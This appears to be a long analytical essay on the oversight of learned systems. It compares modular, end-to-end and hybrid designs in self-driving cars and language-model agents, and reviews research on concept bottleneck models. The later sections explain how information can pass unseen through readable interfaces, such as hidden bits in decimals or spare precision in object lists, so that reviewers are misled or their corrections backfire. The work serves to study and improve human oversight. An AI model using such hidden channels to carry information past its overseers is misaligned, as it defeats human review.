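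### Language agents without a fixed workflow

Some developers of language-model agents have made a similar move. In 2025, the Chinese laboratory Moonshot AI introduced a research agent called Kimi-Researcher. Moonshot AI's *Kimi Researcher* contrasts the agent with workflows that assign roles to several agents and coordinate them through prompts. The drawback of these workflows, according to ThakiCloud's *Complete Analysis of Moonshot AI Kimi-Researcher*, is that people must write the coordination by hand, fit it to a particular model version and revise it whenever the environment changes.

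Moonshot dropped the assigned roles and used reinforcement learning to train one model on the whole task. Its description of the agent comes down to a loop:

sₜ → (thinkₜ, actionₜ)

sₜ₊₁ = context_manager(sₜ, thinkₜ, resultₜ)

The first state, s₀, contains the instructions, a list of tools and the user's question. At each step the model writes its reasoning, then either calls a tool or finishes. An ordinary program, the context manager, combines the tool's result with what came before, and the loop repeats. Moonshot AI's *Kimi Deep Research Overview* reports an average of 23 reasoning steps per task.

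An agent trained end to end would have no planner instructing it to extract the March payments first. It would choose whether to start from the bank statement or the ledger, and training would favour whichever habits led to good final results. Unlike a driving network, it would still leave a readable record. Its tool calls would also be a bottleneck, because it could change the ledger only through them. The reviewer would lose the plan fixed in advance and the acceptance check after every subtask.

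Moonshot's next model brought modules back in a different form. *Kimi K2.5* (2026) explains that when an agent calls its tools one after another, each step adds delay, which eventually limits what the agent can attempt. The paper says the newer model creates its own sub-agents and runs them in parallel "without any predefined subagents or workflow", which cuts execution time by up to a factor of 4.5. A reviewer could read what these sub-agents report. But nobody can test them beforehand, the way they could test Autoware's run-out module, because the sub-agents don't exist until the run begins.

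Anthropic has removed parts of a scaffold without training a new agent for the purpose. The scaffold in *Harness design for long-running application development* (Rajasekaran, 2026) builds complete applications, with one agent to write the program and another to evaluate it. An earlier version also divided the writing into short stages called sprints. Claude Sonnet 4.5 needed them because it tended to wrap up early as its context filled, a tendency called "context anxiety". *The Latticework* (2026) recounts that Rajasekaran removed the sprints because they had become unnecessary overhead with Claude Opus 4.6. His general principle is that every component of a scaffold "encodes an assumption about what the model can't do on its own".

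In one trial, the writing agent worked on a music-editing program for about four hours without sprints, but with the evaluator still in place. According to BestHub's *How Anthropic’s Harness Keeps Long‑Running AI Agents on Track*, the evaluator found unfinished audio controls and timeline segments that users could not drag. The stronger model could work without having its task divided for it, but it still benefited from a separate check.

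Anthropic's *Agent Harness Design* describes how developers can also let the model decide which tool results enter its context, by having it write code that calls the tools and filters their output. This raised Opus 4.6's accuracy on BrowseComp, a test of web research, from 45.3% to 61.6%. For the account, the model might write one script that fetches the payments, matches them to the ledger and prints only the leftovers. The intermediate tables would no longer appear in the conversation, but the reviewer could read and rerun the script, which is arguably better evidence than a worker's note saying that the totals agree.

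### The bitter lesson

Understanding AI reports that Tesla and Wayve expect to win because of the "bitter lesson", a phrase from a 2019 essay by Richard Sutton, a founder of modern reinforcement learning. Sutton argues that AI researchers keep building their own understanding of a problem into their programs, which satisfies them and helps at first. Then progress levels off, and a more general method that can use more computing power, through search or learning, overtakes them. He traces this pattern through chess, Go, speech recognition and computer vision. Hand-written driving rules and fixed agent workflows look like further examples.

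Sutton's lesson has a good record as a forecast of performance, but it has no timeline. Waymo has kept its modules and, as Shirouzu reports, sells rides in about a dozen cities. It also trains those modules jointly on large amounts of data, so it already follows much of Sutton's advice.

The lesson has little direct bearing on oversight. A single network could drive better than any modular car and still fail without warning. A part that exists so that people can check the system may be worth keeping even if it lowers performance. Requiring a person to approve large corrections to an account slows the agent down, but the company accepts the delay for the sake of the check. Asking whether the model still needs a component, as Rajasekaran's principle recommends, is a sensible way to simplify a scaffold. It calls for the same caution, because a human reviewer may still need a component long after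 the model can work without it.

Sutton's argument matters more indirectly, because if modular agents fall far enough behind, few people will use them or be protected by their readable interfaces. The argument can also apply to oversight. More computing power lets Tesla replay more scenes, but it doesn't help an engineer read lists of objects any faster. Testing the whole system might therefore improve more quickly than inspecting its parts, though that advantage is shrinking because language models can now read logs too.

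### Judging the whole machine

Kendall makes the claim about oversight most directly, calling it "naive" to expect a complex intelligent machine to be interpretable enough that someone could trace its behaviour to one line of code or one cause. He thinks people should come to understand such machines through data. He doesn't believe that more training data alone will make a car safe. He also wants an architecture designed for safety and a behavioural safety case, a structured argument, backed by evidence of how the car behaves, that the car is acceptably safe for a stated use.

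He is also sceptical of putting hand-written constraints around a learned driver, which he says often combines the worst of both approaches. Wayve's vice president of AI, Vijay Badrinarayanan, explained to Shirouzu that pre-programmed safety logic "becomes brittle" in situations its authors did not foresee.

This argument has some merit. A car can hit someone because it was going too fast for the street, even though every module worked correctly. After a collision like the one in Santa Monica, logs showing no fault in any module would not settle whether the car was cautious enough. Modular stacks also contain learned networks, so their logs can show that perception missed a pedestrian without showing why.

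But Kendall holds modules to a higher standard than their defenders do. An engineer rarely needs to trace a failure to a single line of code. It is often enough to know that perception failed and planning did not, because the engineer can then repair perception and test it again. Reppert and colleagues traced 51 errors to one step and replaced that step without an explanation of their language model's inner workings.

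Testing the whole system is also expensive, for the reason Shalev-Shwartz and Shashua gave. Elluswamy acknowledges that a car can drive safely for a year and then have one failure that stops the whole programme. A large change to the system also weakens the evidence gathered before the change. Koopman told Yoshida that if Waymo moved to an end-to-end design, it would be "a completely different vehicle", and that any claim that its old safety data still applied would be suspect.

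Kendall does expect some inspection, and he imagines regulators questioning a car in ordinary language about its decisions. The car's answers would be readouts, like Tesla's. He thinks end-to-end networks could fairly be called uninterpretable five or ten years ago, but not now. At least one customer, Nissan, is not yet comfortable with Wayve's system, which it plans to use in a van in Japan by March 2028. Nissan's technology chief, Eiichi Akashi, told Shirouzu that the system is the "most advanced" but that it is "difficult to peer into it and see how it makes decisions".

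Wayve's design may be less uniform than the company suggests. Understanding AI noticed a "safety expert sub-system" in Wayve's architecture diagram but could find no details of how it works. If that sub-system can overrule the rest of the network, Wayve would have kept a module where oversight matters most, and engineers could test it separately.

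## Joint training with readable outputs: the hybrid position

Waymo combines the two approaches. It trains its driving modules together but also has them output objects and roads in a form that people and ordinary programs can use. General Motors and NVIDIA have published related designs since late 2025. All three companies accept that a list of objects leaves out too much information for driving, so they keep the list and add other channels between perception and planning.

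### Waymo's two encoders and one decoder

According to Axios, Waymo in its early years had a separate model for each narrow job, such as detecting pedestrians or telling when a light turned green. Waymo's *Demonstrably Safe AI For Autonomous Driving*, published in December 2025, describes a design with three large parts. Two encoders turn raw input into a description of the scene, and a decoder turns that description into predictions and a plan.

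The sensor fusion encoder is the fast one. It combines camera, lidar and radar data over time and produces objects, labels and embeddings, which are learned vectors with no fixed meaning for a human reader. Dolgov told Understanding AI that speed matters here when, for example, an object appears from behind a parked car.

The other encoder is a vision-language model, which takes in images and text. Waymo trained it using Google's Gemini so that it could draw on general knowledge of the world. Waymo's example is a burning vehicle on the road ahead. The lanes around it may be clear, so a system that checks only for free space would drive past. The vision-language model can send a signal that prompts the car to turn round or take another route.

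Both encoders feed the World Decoder, which predicts what other road users will do, draws a detailed map and generates trajectories for the car. Training can use errors in the decoder's output to adjust all the parts.

For the pedestrian behind the van, the fast encoder might output a class, position and speed. Its embedding could also carry details missing from that record, such as the phone in the person's hand, without an engineer adding a field for them. Other software can still use the explicit part of the output, which Waymo describes as objects, semantic attributes and elements of the road layout.

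The full model is too big to run in a car, so Waymo trains a smaller "student" model to imitate a large "teacher", a method called distillation. The student has the same structure as the full model, so the model in the car is also divided into parts.

In *10 AI Lessons from Driving 200+ Million Fully Autonomous Miles* (August 2026), Waymo defends this design against both alternatives. It calls the old collection of specialised models "modular spaghetti" that nobody can maintain at scale. It argues, much as Sutton does, that fewer, larger models let the data, rather than "brittle human priors", determine what is relevant. But Waymo also rejects a single black box, because it is hard to understand how such a system makes decisions. Its remedy is a separate layer that checks every proposed trajectory. That layer can stop a bad plan but doesn't explain it, so any explanation would have to come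 from the written structures.

### UniAD's learned queries

The research precursor to these designs is UniAD, which Hu, Yang and colleagues built to find out which intermediate tasks help a planner and how to connect them (*Planning-oriented Autonomous Driving*, 2023).

UniAD first converts its camera images into a grid of the scene from above, in which each cell holds a learned vector. A tracking module then keeps another vector, called a query, for each road user, and a mapping module keeps one for each lane, divider or crossing. A motion module uses both sets of queries to predict where each road user will go, and an occupancy module predicts which cells will be occupied. The planner starts from a query that represents the car itself, adds a command to turn left, turn right or keep going, uses the grid again and produces a path.

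Engineers can decode a box from the query that represents a pedestrian, and training penalises errors in that box. But the next module receives the query rather than the box. Hu and colleagues preferred queries because they draw on a wider area of the scene than a box does, which reduces the effect of upstream mistakes.

In their tests, a planner trained without any intermediate tasks had a collision rate of 0.77%. The rate fell to 0.43% with all the tasks connected, but rose to 0.94% when the tasks shared the grid and were not connected to each other.

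Hu and colleagues also describe a case in which the plan stayed reasonable although the tracker had missed some objects or badly misjudged which way they were facing. They count this as a success for the design, and it does benefit passengers. But because the planner uses the grid directly, it can act on things that someone reading the list of objects wouldn't see there, such as a pedestrian the tracker missed.

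One readable output did have a direct influence on the plan. After the planner had produced a path, a separate calculation adjusted it to minimise

cost = λ₁ · (distance from the planner's path) + λ₂ · (closeness to cells predicted to be full).

If an engineer marked a cell as full, the path would move away from it. Hu and colleagues found that moving the path away from full cells cut the collision rate three seconds ahead from 1.39% to 1.05%.

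### Switching the readable outputs off

In *PARA-Drive*, Weng, Ivanovic and colleagues (2024) examined the connections in UniAD one by one. They first corrected how researchers scored such systems. UniAD's scoring method ignored the car's heading and used a coarse grid, so it counted the paths that human drivers had actually taken as collisions 0.38% of the time.

Under better scoring, UniAD drove worse with the adjustment based on the occupancy map, the one place where a readable map could overrule the planner. Removing the adjustment lowered the collision rate from 0.40% to 0.16%, because it had often produced zigzag paths near groups of objects. Also removing a noisy link between mapping and motion prediction lowered the rate to 0.13%.

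Weng and colleagues then removed the planner's access to the grid and compared how well it planned with readable outputs and with learned vectors. The error in the table is the average distance between the planned path and the human driver's path over the next three seconds.

| What the planner receives, besides the route command | Collision rate | Average error |
|---|---|---|
| Grid and vectors for road users | 0.13% | 0.53 m |
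| Nothing | 5.88% | 4.66 m |
| Boxes for road users | 0.97% | 1.10 m |
| Vectors for road users | 0.14% | 0.54 m |
| Readable road map | 1.22% | 1.59 m |
| Vectors for road elements | 0.20% | 0.58 m |

The planner did almost as well with vectors for road users as it did with the grid. When it received boxes for the same road users instead, it had about seven times as many collisions. The strangest result is in the last row, where the planner rarely hit other road users even though it received only vectors that are supposed to describe lanes and crossings.

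One possible explanation is that the vectors also carried the car's own speed. Weng and colleagues tested a simple network whose only inputs were the car's own state and past movement, with no camera data. It had the same collision rate, 0.20%, and nearly the same error, because most of the recordings show a car going straight ahead. Whatever the vectors contained, a reader who took them as a description of the road would have missed something the planner used.

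The final PARA-Drive design removes every link between the readable modules and the planner. Mapping, motion prediction and occupancy prediction run alongside planning, and all four modules read the same grid. After training, engineers can switch off the three readable modules, or run them only occasionally for a safety check or a display. The planner then runs 2.77 times faster than UniAD and produces the same plans as it does with them on.

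A readout is an output that engineers can remove without changing the plan. PARA-Drive's object list, road map and occupancy map are all readouts.

Leaving the same tasks out of training had a large effect. Without occupancy prediction, the collision rate rose from 0.20% to 0.64%, and the share of planned positions that were off the road rose from 0.32% to 4.19%. Dropping motion prediction had a similar effect. Dropping the mapping task left collisions roughly unchanged but more than doubled the off-road share. Learning to draw boxes and roads evidently improved the grid the planner relies on, so developers have a practical reason to train readable outputs even if they don't care about oversight.

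These results need some caution because Weng and colleagues used open-loop tests, which compare a planned path with a recording and never let the car act on its plan, so an early mistake can't lead to a worse situation later. *DriveTransformer* (2025) argues that such tests cannot reflect real planning ability. The camera-less network's results support this objection. It matched PARA-Drive's average error across all the recordings, but on turns and lane changes its collision rate was 0.94%, against 0.14% for PARA-Drive. There is also other evidence for joint training. In *UniTeD* (2026), for instance, a system that learned perception and planning together scored 2.8 points higher on a planning benchmark than one that kept them separate.

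### GM gives the planner both

General Motors' *Compound AI* (2026) uses the same label as Mobileye for a different design. Mobileye's engineers develop the layers independently, while GM lets corrections to the trajectory flow back into a shared encoder. The encoder produces embeddings, which perception decoders turn into maps and tracks (records of each road user over time). The trajectory generator receives all three. Guardrails then apply limits based on physics, drivable space and safety margins.

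GM considered putting guardrails around a purely end-to-end model but decided that the model would still be hard to inspect and validate. It uses the perception decoders to solve that problem. They also help with training, because GM can penalise a trajectory that runs into a tracked object or crosses a road boundary.

GM expects the readable outputs to allow "clearer attribution when something goes wrong", but gives no measurements. Suppose the tracks show the pedestrian in the right place and the car still fails to brake. In a separately trained stack where the planner sees only the tracks, the engineer could rule out perception as the cause. In GM's design, the trajectory generator could have relied on embeddings that failed to represent the pedestrian, so the engineer would still have to investigate perception.

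### NVIDIA adds a sentence of explanation

NVIDIA's Alpamayo is a vision-language-action model, meaning a single model takes in images and text and produces both language and physical actions. Its readable output is a short causal explanation, which for the van might be "yield to the pedestrian stepping out from behind the parked van". The default prompt, reproduced in *Latency Analysis and Optimization of Alpamayo 1 via Efficient Trajectory Generation* (2026), calls for the reasoning first and then the trajectory.

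*Alpamayo-R1* (2025) describes how NVIDIA made these explanations more specific than the advice to "be cautious" that is common in older datasets. Each training example names at most one decision about speed, such as yielding or following the car ahead, and at most one about position, such as changing lanes. Both come from a fixed list of 15. The causes can be anything relevant, but annotators must choose them from the two seconds of video before the decision. They watch the next six seconds, to see what the driver did, only after choosing the causes. This prevents an explanation from citing something that had not happened yet.

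People checked only about a tenth of the examples, and models such as GPT-5 labelled the rest. Neither the annotators nor the models had the driver's own explanation, so Alpamayo learns from reasons that an observer found plausible.

A smaller network, the action expert, produces the final trajectory. In about ten steps, it refines random noise into 64 pairs of acceleration and curvature values, which together cover about six seconds. At every step it reads the language model's internal state for the whole sequence, which includes the camera images and the car's recent motion as well as the explanation. The action expert can therefore use information that the explanation omits. For example, it could react to the pedestrian in the images even if the explanation didn't mention one.

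The model's parts are also not trained entirely together. The language model learns to predict both the explanation and a coded version of the trajectory, but NVIDIA prevents the action expert's training from changing it. Reinforcement learning later rewards explanations that agree with the trajectory. A later section covers tests of whether the explanations influence how the car drives.

NVIDIA released the newest version, Alpamayo 2 Super, in August 2026. It has 34 billion parameters and can also output its decision in a few words, such as "yield" or "stop". NVIDIA suggests that a separate planner could act on that decision, or that a program could compare it with the shape of the trajectory. The company also argues that having both an explanation and a trajectory helps developers tell whether a failure began in perception, reasoning or action.

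NVIDIA's *Taking Alpamayo to New Heights with Driving Foundation Models and Closed-Loop Training* proposes, as one of the main uses for the model, training smaller models offline for use in cars. If a small model brakes and the large model later explains the scene, the explanation is the large model's own interpretation, and the small model may have braked for a different reason.

### How much travels in the vectors

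Waymo's public documents don't show how much of the information behind a driving decision is in the embeddings and how much is in the written structures. *ML at Waymo* (Tsui, 2026), a set of slides by the head of the company's machine-learning platform, includes a diagram that labels the fast encoder's output "Objects, sensor embeddings". For the vision-language model, the diagram lists embeddings along with "Semantics, rationales & text tokens". This suggests that the decoder receives both kinds of information.

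The decoder produces the plan from both vectors and written structures, and how much the structures help oversight depends on how it uses them. If it used only the structures, they would be a bottleneck, and a reviewer could read everything the plan depended on. If it used only the vectors, the structures would be readouts, as in PARA-Drive. Waymo's system could be anywhere between the two, and the balance could change with the situation. For example, the decoder might rely on the object list in ordinary traffic and on a vector from the vision-language model when a vehicle is on fire.

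Waymo could test this by deleting the pedestrian from s, leaving v unchanged, and checking whether the car still brakes. The result would need careful interpretation, because the decoder would receive two contradictory descriptions, which it may never have encountered in training. Smaller changes, such as moving the pedestrian by half a metre, would be less artificial. Weng and colleagues avoided the contradiction by training a new planner for each kind of input. Their results show what a planner can do with boxes or vectors alone, but not how much an existing planner relies on each when it has both.

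### What an incomplete record is good for

The best defense of the hybrid position is that the written structures don't need to be complete to be useful. In its December account, Waymo lists three uses for them: simulation, feedback during training and safety checks while the car is driving.

Readable objects help with simulation because engineers can edit them. To test what the car would do if the pedestrian stepped out half a second earlier, they can change one entry and have Waymo's simulator generate matching camera and lidar data. With an embedding, they wouldn't know which numbers to change. As with Tesla's simulator, the test measures what the car does, so it remains valid even if the planner relies entirely on embeddings.

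For training, Waymo uses a separate model, the Critic, to look for bad driving on the road and in simulation. A pedestrian's recorded position and the car's planned path are enough to calculate how close the car would come to the pedestrian. Training can use that distance as a reward or penalty, and an engineer who disputes it can repeat the calculation.

The car can run the same calculation before it moves. If the planned path crosses a pedestrian on the list, a checking program can reject the path without any explanation of why the decoder produced it. The list is therefore useful for control even where it doesn't explain the plan.

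Checking a planned path against the system's list of detected objects works well for catching errors that the list reveals. But passing the check is much weaker evidence of safety than failing it is of a problem, because a pass shows only that the path avoids everything on the list. In Waymo's design, the fast encoder produces both the objects and the sensor embeddings. If it misses a child between two parked cars, the plan may not account for the child, and the child may also be missing from the list that a program uses to check the plan.

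## Can information bypass the readable interface?

The diagram of Waymo's design shows the bypass, where learned vectors reach the decoder alongside the list of objects. Even without the vectors, a reader of the list might miss some of the information passed to the decoder, because the readable values can themselves carry information beyond their stated meaning.

Researchers have studied this kind of leakage most closely in concept bottleneck models, which have only two modules. The interface between them is a list of concepts named by people.

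### Two networks and a list of concepts

The usual test case is CUB, a collection of 11,788 photographs of 200 bird species. A concept network estimates whether a photograph shows each of 112 attributes, such as a red wing or a hooked beak. An answer network then names the species from those estimates alone. If the estimate for "hooked beak" is wrong, a birdwatcher can correct it and rerun the answer network.

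The estimates can be hard (yes or no) or soft (probabilities such as 0.93).

In 2020, Koh and colleagues set out three ways to train the two networks. *Leakage and Interpretability in Concept-Based Models* (Parisini, Chakraborti and colleagues, 2025) describes them as follows.

| Training | What the concept network learns from | What the answer network learns from |
|---|---|---|
| Independent | True concepts | True concepts and answers |
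| Sequential | True concepts | The finished concept network's estimates, and answers |
| Joint | True concepts and errors in the final answer | The concept network's estimates as they change, and answers |

Joint training minimises L(answer) + λ · L(concepts), the same kind of weighted sum that can keep objects readable in a jointly trained driving system. In independent training, neither network adapts to the other.

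### One bit in the decimals

Makonnen, Vandenhirtz and colleagues (2025), in *Measuring Leakage in Concept-Based Methods*, define leakage as the information that the soft values give about the answer beyond what the concepts themselves give:

I(Y; S | C) = H(Y | C) − H(Y | S, C).

Here Y is the answer, S the soft values and C the hard concepts. H measures uncertainty in bits, so the formula gives how much uncertainty about the answer falls when someone who already knows the hard concepts also sees the soft values.

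A very small system shows how this can happen. Toss two fair coins, a and b. The concept is a, and the answer that the system must predict is b. Since the coins are independent, knowing a gives 0 bits about b. Suppose the concept network produces these values:

| a | b | Soft value for a | Rounded |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 1 | 0.99 | 1 |
| 1 | 0 | 0.90 | 1 |
| 0 | 1 | 0.10 | 0 |
| 0 | 0 | 0.01 | 0 |

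The rounded value is always right, so concept accuracy is perfect. But the answer network can also recover b from the exact value. Uncertainty about b falls from 1 bit to 0, so 1 bit leaks. A person who saw 0.90 displayed would probably read it as slight doubt about a.

Leakage also interferes with corrections. Suppose a reviewer checks the first coin, sees that a is 1, and replaces 0.90 with 1. If the answer network treats 1 like 0.99, it changes its prediction for b from 0, which was correct, to 1. If reviewers confirmed every value this way, the system's accuracy would fall from 100% to 50%.

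Joint training rewards this code. With the usual logarithmic error, using 0.90 and 0.99 in place of a perfect 1 adds about 0.058 to the concept error, while knowing b removes 0.693 from the answer error. The code therefore lowers the total error unless λ is above about 12. If the two values were 0.990 and 0.999 instead, λ would have to be above about 125. Raising λ makes leakage smaller and harder to notice, but joint training still rewards it.

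Parisini and colleagues found a similar pattern in trained models. Leakage fell as they raised λ, then levelled off above zero. Above a λ of about 10, the models often failed to learn the final task properly.

### Leakage without joint training

Margeloiu and colleagues showed in 2021 that the outputs of concept networks contain more information than the concepts they stand for. They blamed this on joint training and suggested training the concept network without reference to the final task. Later that year, Mahinpei, Clark and colleagues tried this in *Promises and Pitfalls of Black-Box Concept Learning Models* and found that information still leaked.

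Mahinpei and colleagues trained a model to tell whether a handwritten digit was odd or even using two concepts, "is a four" and "is a five". They removed all the fours and fives from the data, so the true value of both concepts was always no. Someone given only those true values could do no better than guess, and would be right half the time. The researchers trained the concept network first, froze it, and then trained the answer network on the soft values it produced. The answer network was right 69% of the time.

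The concept network was not trained to tell odd numbers from even ones, but its soft value for "four" depends on how far an image is from the boundary between fours and everything else. A nine might get 0.002 and a zero 0.00001, since a nine looks more like a four. The values for "four" closely followed the main way in which the images differed, and that one dimension was enough to tell odd from even 86% of the time. The answer network learned to use this information, which was a by-product of estimating a probability.

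Leakage gets worse when the list of concepts is incomplete. In another experiment, Mahinpei and colleagues trained models to predict whether at least two of three independent quantities were positive, but gave them concepts for only two of the quantities. They scored predictions on a scale where 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. A network given the true values of the two concepts scored 0.875, while a jointly trained concept model scored 0.999. Each of the concept model's two soft values also predicted the missing third concept, with a score of about 0.75.

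Mahinpei and colleagues added a third, unlabelled unit to hold the missing information, but it did not reliably capture the missing concept and sometimes contained information about the other two concepts.

### Measuring what gets through

Ordinary test accuracy does not reveal leakage. Parisini and colleagues trained two models on pictures of simple shapes, one with λ = 0.1 and the other with λ = 0.01. Both predicted the concepts and the answers perfectly. When they replaced the soft values with the true concepts, the first model's accuracy did not change. After the same replacement, the second scored 67 percentage points below an answer network trained on true concepts.

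Makonnen and colleagues train two classifiers to detect such differences directly. One predicts the answer from the true concepts, and the other also gets the soft values. They estimate the leakage by how much the second classifier improves on the first. On artificial data where they controlled the true amount of leakage, the estimate generally rose and fell with it, but it was noisy and occasionally negative, which is impossible for real leakage.

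Parisini and colleagues calculate a score for each concept separately:

leakage of concept i = max(0, [I(Sᵢ; Y) − I(Cᵢ; Y)] / H(Y)).

In the coin example, the score is (1 − 0)/1 = 1, the maximum. The average score was close to zero for models with hard values and independent training. Across eight datasets, the score correlated at 0.49 to 0.84 with the accuracy that models lost when they received the true concepts. *CBM-Bench* (2026), a benchmark for concept models, has adopted the score.

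This kind of score can miss information that is spread over several concepts. Suppose a network shifts two soft values in the same direction when b is 1 and in opposite directions when b is 0. Neither value alone would carry information about b, so both scores would be zero, but the answer network could still recover b from the pair. Makonnen and colleagues' estimate uses all the values together and could detect this, given a good enough classifier.

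A model can also score low on leakage because it bypasses its concepts. *Measuring What Matters* (2026) reports leakage of 0.052 for an ordinary concept bottleneck model and only 0.002 for an "energy-based" one. The energy-based model's concepts carry no extra information because it predicts the answer from the image rather than from them. A leakage score therefore needs to be paired with a correction test, which shows whether the concepts affect the answer.

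Park (2026), in *Latent Class Concept Bottleneck Models*, uses a more direct test, shuffling the concept labels among the images before training. A photograph of a lorry might get the labels for a tulip, so the labels no longer carry any information about the image or the answer. If a model's predictions depend on what its concepts mean, its accuracy should drop to chance, which is 1% on CIFAR-100, a set of small images in 100 categories.

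| Model, trained on shuffled concepts | Accuracy on CIFAR-100 |
|---|---|
| Hard concepts | 1.0% |
| Stochastic model, which represents links between concepts | 5.0% |
| Label-free model | 65.3% |

A label-free model needs no hand-labeled images because it gets its concepts from a language model and uses a vision-language model to score each image against them. Its accuracy barely changed when the concept names were made meaningless. Its answer network was evidently using the continuous scores as a general description of the image, regardless of the concept names, so anyone reading those names as the reasons for an answer would have been misled.

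Park's second test supports this interpretation. On CIFAR-10, a similar set with ten categories, setting 50 concepts to their true values raised the hard model's accuracy from 86.8% to 89.3%. The same corrections lowered the label-free model's accuracy from 86.7% to 77.8%.

### Rounding, and training apart

Rounding and independent training are both effective against leakage through decimals. Rounding every value to yes or no removes the decimals before they reach the answer network. In the coin example, 0.90 and 0.99 both become 1, so the answer network has to guess b again. Independent training keeps the decimals, but the answer network cannot learn the code because it has only seen true concepts. Under sequential training it can still learn the code, as the experiment with odd and even digits showed.

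Rounding reduces performance only slightly when the list of concepts covers the task well. Park compared soft and hard models that were otherwise alike, along with a new hard model that accounts for which concepts tend to occur together.

| Dataset | Soft | Hard | Hard, with links between concepts |
|---|---|---|---|
| CUB, 112 concepts | 67.5% | 67.3% | 72.4% |
| CIFAR-10, 143 concepts | 69.6% | 68.8% | 71.5% |
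| CIFAR-100, 892 concepts | 39.3% | 38.0% | 40.0% |

The plain hard model lost at most 1.3 percentage points of accuracy, and the new model more than recovered that loss. On these tasks, accuracy gives developers little reason to accept soft values.

However, rounding does not ensure that a concept means what its name suggests. Eight yes-or-no values are enough to distinguish CUB's 200 species, and the list has 112. A network that recognises the species by any means could fill in the whole list with values memorised for that species, and the answer network could then recover the species from the list.

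Saralajew, Pastor and colleagues (2026) found signs of this in *Auditing Where Concept Bottleneck Accuracy Comes From on CUB*. Developers usually train on labels that are the same for every photograph of a species, so a bird may be labelled "grey tail" in a picture that shows only its head. These labels agree with what annotators saw in each photograph only about 82% of the time. A concept network that matches these labels much more often than that must be inferring some attributes from the species.

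Saralajew and colleagues also trained classifiers on the attributes that annotators had marked in each photograph. The best one named the species correctly 37.5% of the time, while widely used concept models have reported accuracies above 70%. Leakage does not explain the whole gap, because the annotations contain mistakes and yes-or-no labels miss finer differences that the images show. But when they limited each concept to a small patch of the image, the accuracy they could recover from the concept values fell from 72% to 43%, so much of the information about the species had come from elsewhere in the image.

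Even the models limited to small patches often used the bird's head as evidence about its wings, body and tail. If a birdwatcher looked at the tail and corrected "grey tail", they would be changing a value that the answer network had learned to treat as a clue from the head. Hard yes-or-no values would not solve this, because the concept network could still base its yes or no about the tail on the head.

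### The defence of leakage

*In Defense of Information Leakage in Concept-based Models* (Espinosa Zarlenga, 2026) argues that trying to eliminate leakage is a mistake. Outside benchmarks, people can rarely list every concept that matters in advance, and labelling them all would be expensive. For example, a model that has to identify reptiles without a concept for scales will do badly unless it can get the missing information some other way.

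The main experiment uses only 22 of the CUB concepts. A model with independent training and almost no leakage classified 47.6% of the birds correctly. A second model, which had 500 unlabelled units alongside the 22 concepts, classified 73.3% correctly, and its concept estimates were about as good as the first model's.

Espinosa Zarlenga calls leakage "benign" if it meets two conditions. The unlabelled part of the signal must contain what the concepts leave out, and information about a concept must stay in the part that a reviewer changes when correcting that concept. To encourage this, training adds a penalty for wrong answers when all the concepts have their true values. With the penalty, correcting concepts improved the answers of the model with 500 extra units. That model also relied on much the same concepts as the strict one. On average, the two models shared 4.3 of their five most heavily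 weighted inputs for each species, compared with 4.5 for two training runs of the strict model. Without the penalty, they shared only 2.0.

The argument about accuracy is convincing. Few people would use a model that is wrong more than half the time just because they could read its reasons, and a reviewer who had to correct most of its answers would gain little from the list. The experiment also shows that a model can leak a lot of information and still respond sensibly to corrections.

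The argument about explanation is weaker. Espinosa Zarlenga says that when concepts are missing, even a strict model can't fully explain its predictions. But a strict model's answer still follows entirely from the concepts on its list. If it mistakes one bird for another because the list has no entry for eye colour, a reader can see that the two birds have the same entries and work out what is missing. In the model with 500 extra units, the gain of 26 percentage points depends on unlabelled information, and a reader can't tell whether an answer came from the concepts or from the extra units.

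Successful corrections do not show that the readable part is complete, either. Espinosa Zarlenga trained an ordinary network without concept labels for its internal units, but applied the same penalty to 22 of them. The network learned to respond well to corrections even though those units were never its only source of information.

Verghese, Soelistyo and colleagues (2026), in *Harmful Partial Interventions and Benign Leakage in Concept-based Models*, tested whether the corrections are safe. They proved that a model can come arbitrarily close to meeting both conditions for benign leakage and still do much worse after a correction. The answer network may have learned to rely on a particular error in a concept together with something in the unlabelled units. Correcting the concept while leaving those units unchanged produces a combination that did not occur in training. Espinosa Zarlenga had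 already acknowledged that the conditions are not enough, because the answer network must also use the concepts properly.

The penalty covers only the case where every concept is correct, and reviewers seldom check them all. Verghese and colleagues therefore corrected models' 50 bird concepts one at a time, in 512 random orders. Even with the penalty, the model's average error rose above its uncorrected level at some point in 91.2% of these sequences. Adding a penalty for corrections that make the answer worse reduced this to 51.4%, with almost no change in accuracy.

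The harm was common but small. With only the first penalty, error rose by an average of 0.0054 at the worst point in a sequence, and adding the second cut this increase to 0.0004. By comparison, correcting all the concepts in a model trained with neither penalty raised its error by 0.0198. The harm was greater when the concepts left out more of what mattered, which is when Espinosa Zarlenga recommends allowing leakage.

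How much this matters depends on why someone is reading the concepts. Parisini and colleagues describe a model that recommends cancer treatment using concepts from a biopsy, such as how aggressive the tumour looks. The right treatment also depends on whether the cancer has spread, but the model has no concept for that. If it encodes information about the spread in its value for the tumour's appearance, a doctor who corrects that value could unknowingly change the information about the spread too. In a birdwatching app, the extra accuracy matters more than a complete explanation, but for the doctor it would be better to add the missing concept, or at least to put the extra information in a separate channel and show that it exists. Parisini and colleagues go further and advise against using concept models where the list of concepts is incomplete and nobody can extend it.

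### Object lists and text messages

Most of these experiments used image classifiers, so they are weak evidence of how much a driving system leaks. But information can leak this way whenever values have more precision than a reader pays attention to and a second module has learned from those values. A list of objects with positions, speeds and confidence scores has that extra precision. Two spare decimal digits can hold up to 6.6 bits, so a list of 30 objects with six such numbers each has room for about 1,200 bits that nobody would notice.

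Whether a planner uses that room depends on its design. A hand-written rule that brakes when a distance falls below 15 metres can't decode a hidden message, although the distance may still be wrong. A learned planner trained on the output of a finished detector can learn to use extra information in that output, like the network that learned to tell odd from even. It might learn that the detector's confidence drops in fog and start using confidence as a measure of visibility. That could make the car safer, but an engineer reading "pedestrian, 0.81" would not know that the planner was also using the number to judge visibility and adjust the car's speed.

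Joint training through the list adds a direct incentive to leak information. The higher collision rate of PARA-Drive's box-fed planner suggests that boxes omit much of what a planner needs, so the incentive is probably strong. Engineers could check for leaks by rounding positions to the nearest ten centimetres and dropping the confidence scores. If the car then drives much worse than the lost precision can explain, the planner was using information the list did not appear to contain. Rounding would not catch every leak. Mahinpei and colleagues found that a modest number of meaningless yes-or-no values can together describe an image surprisingly well.

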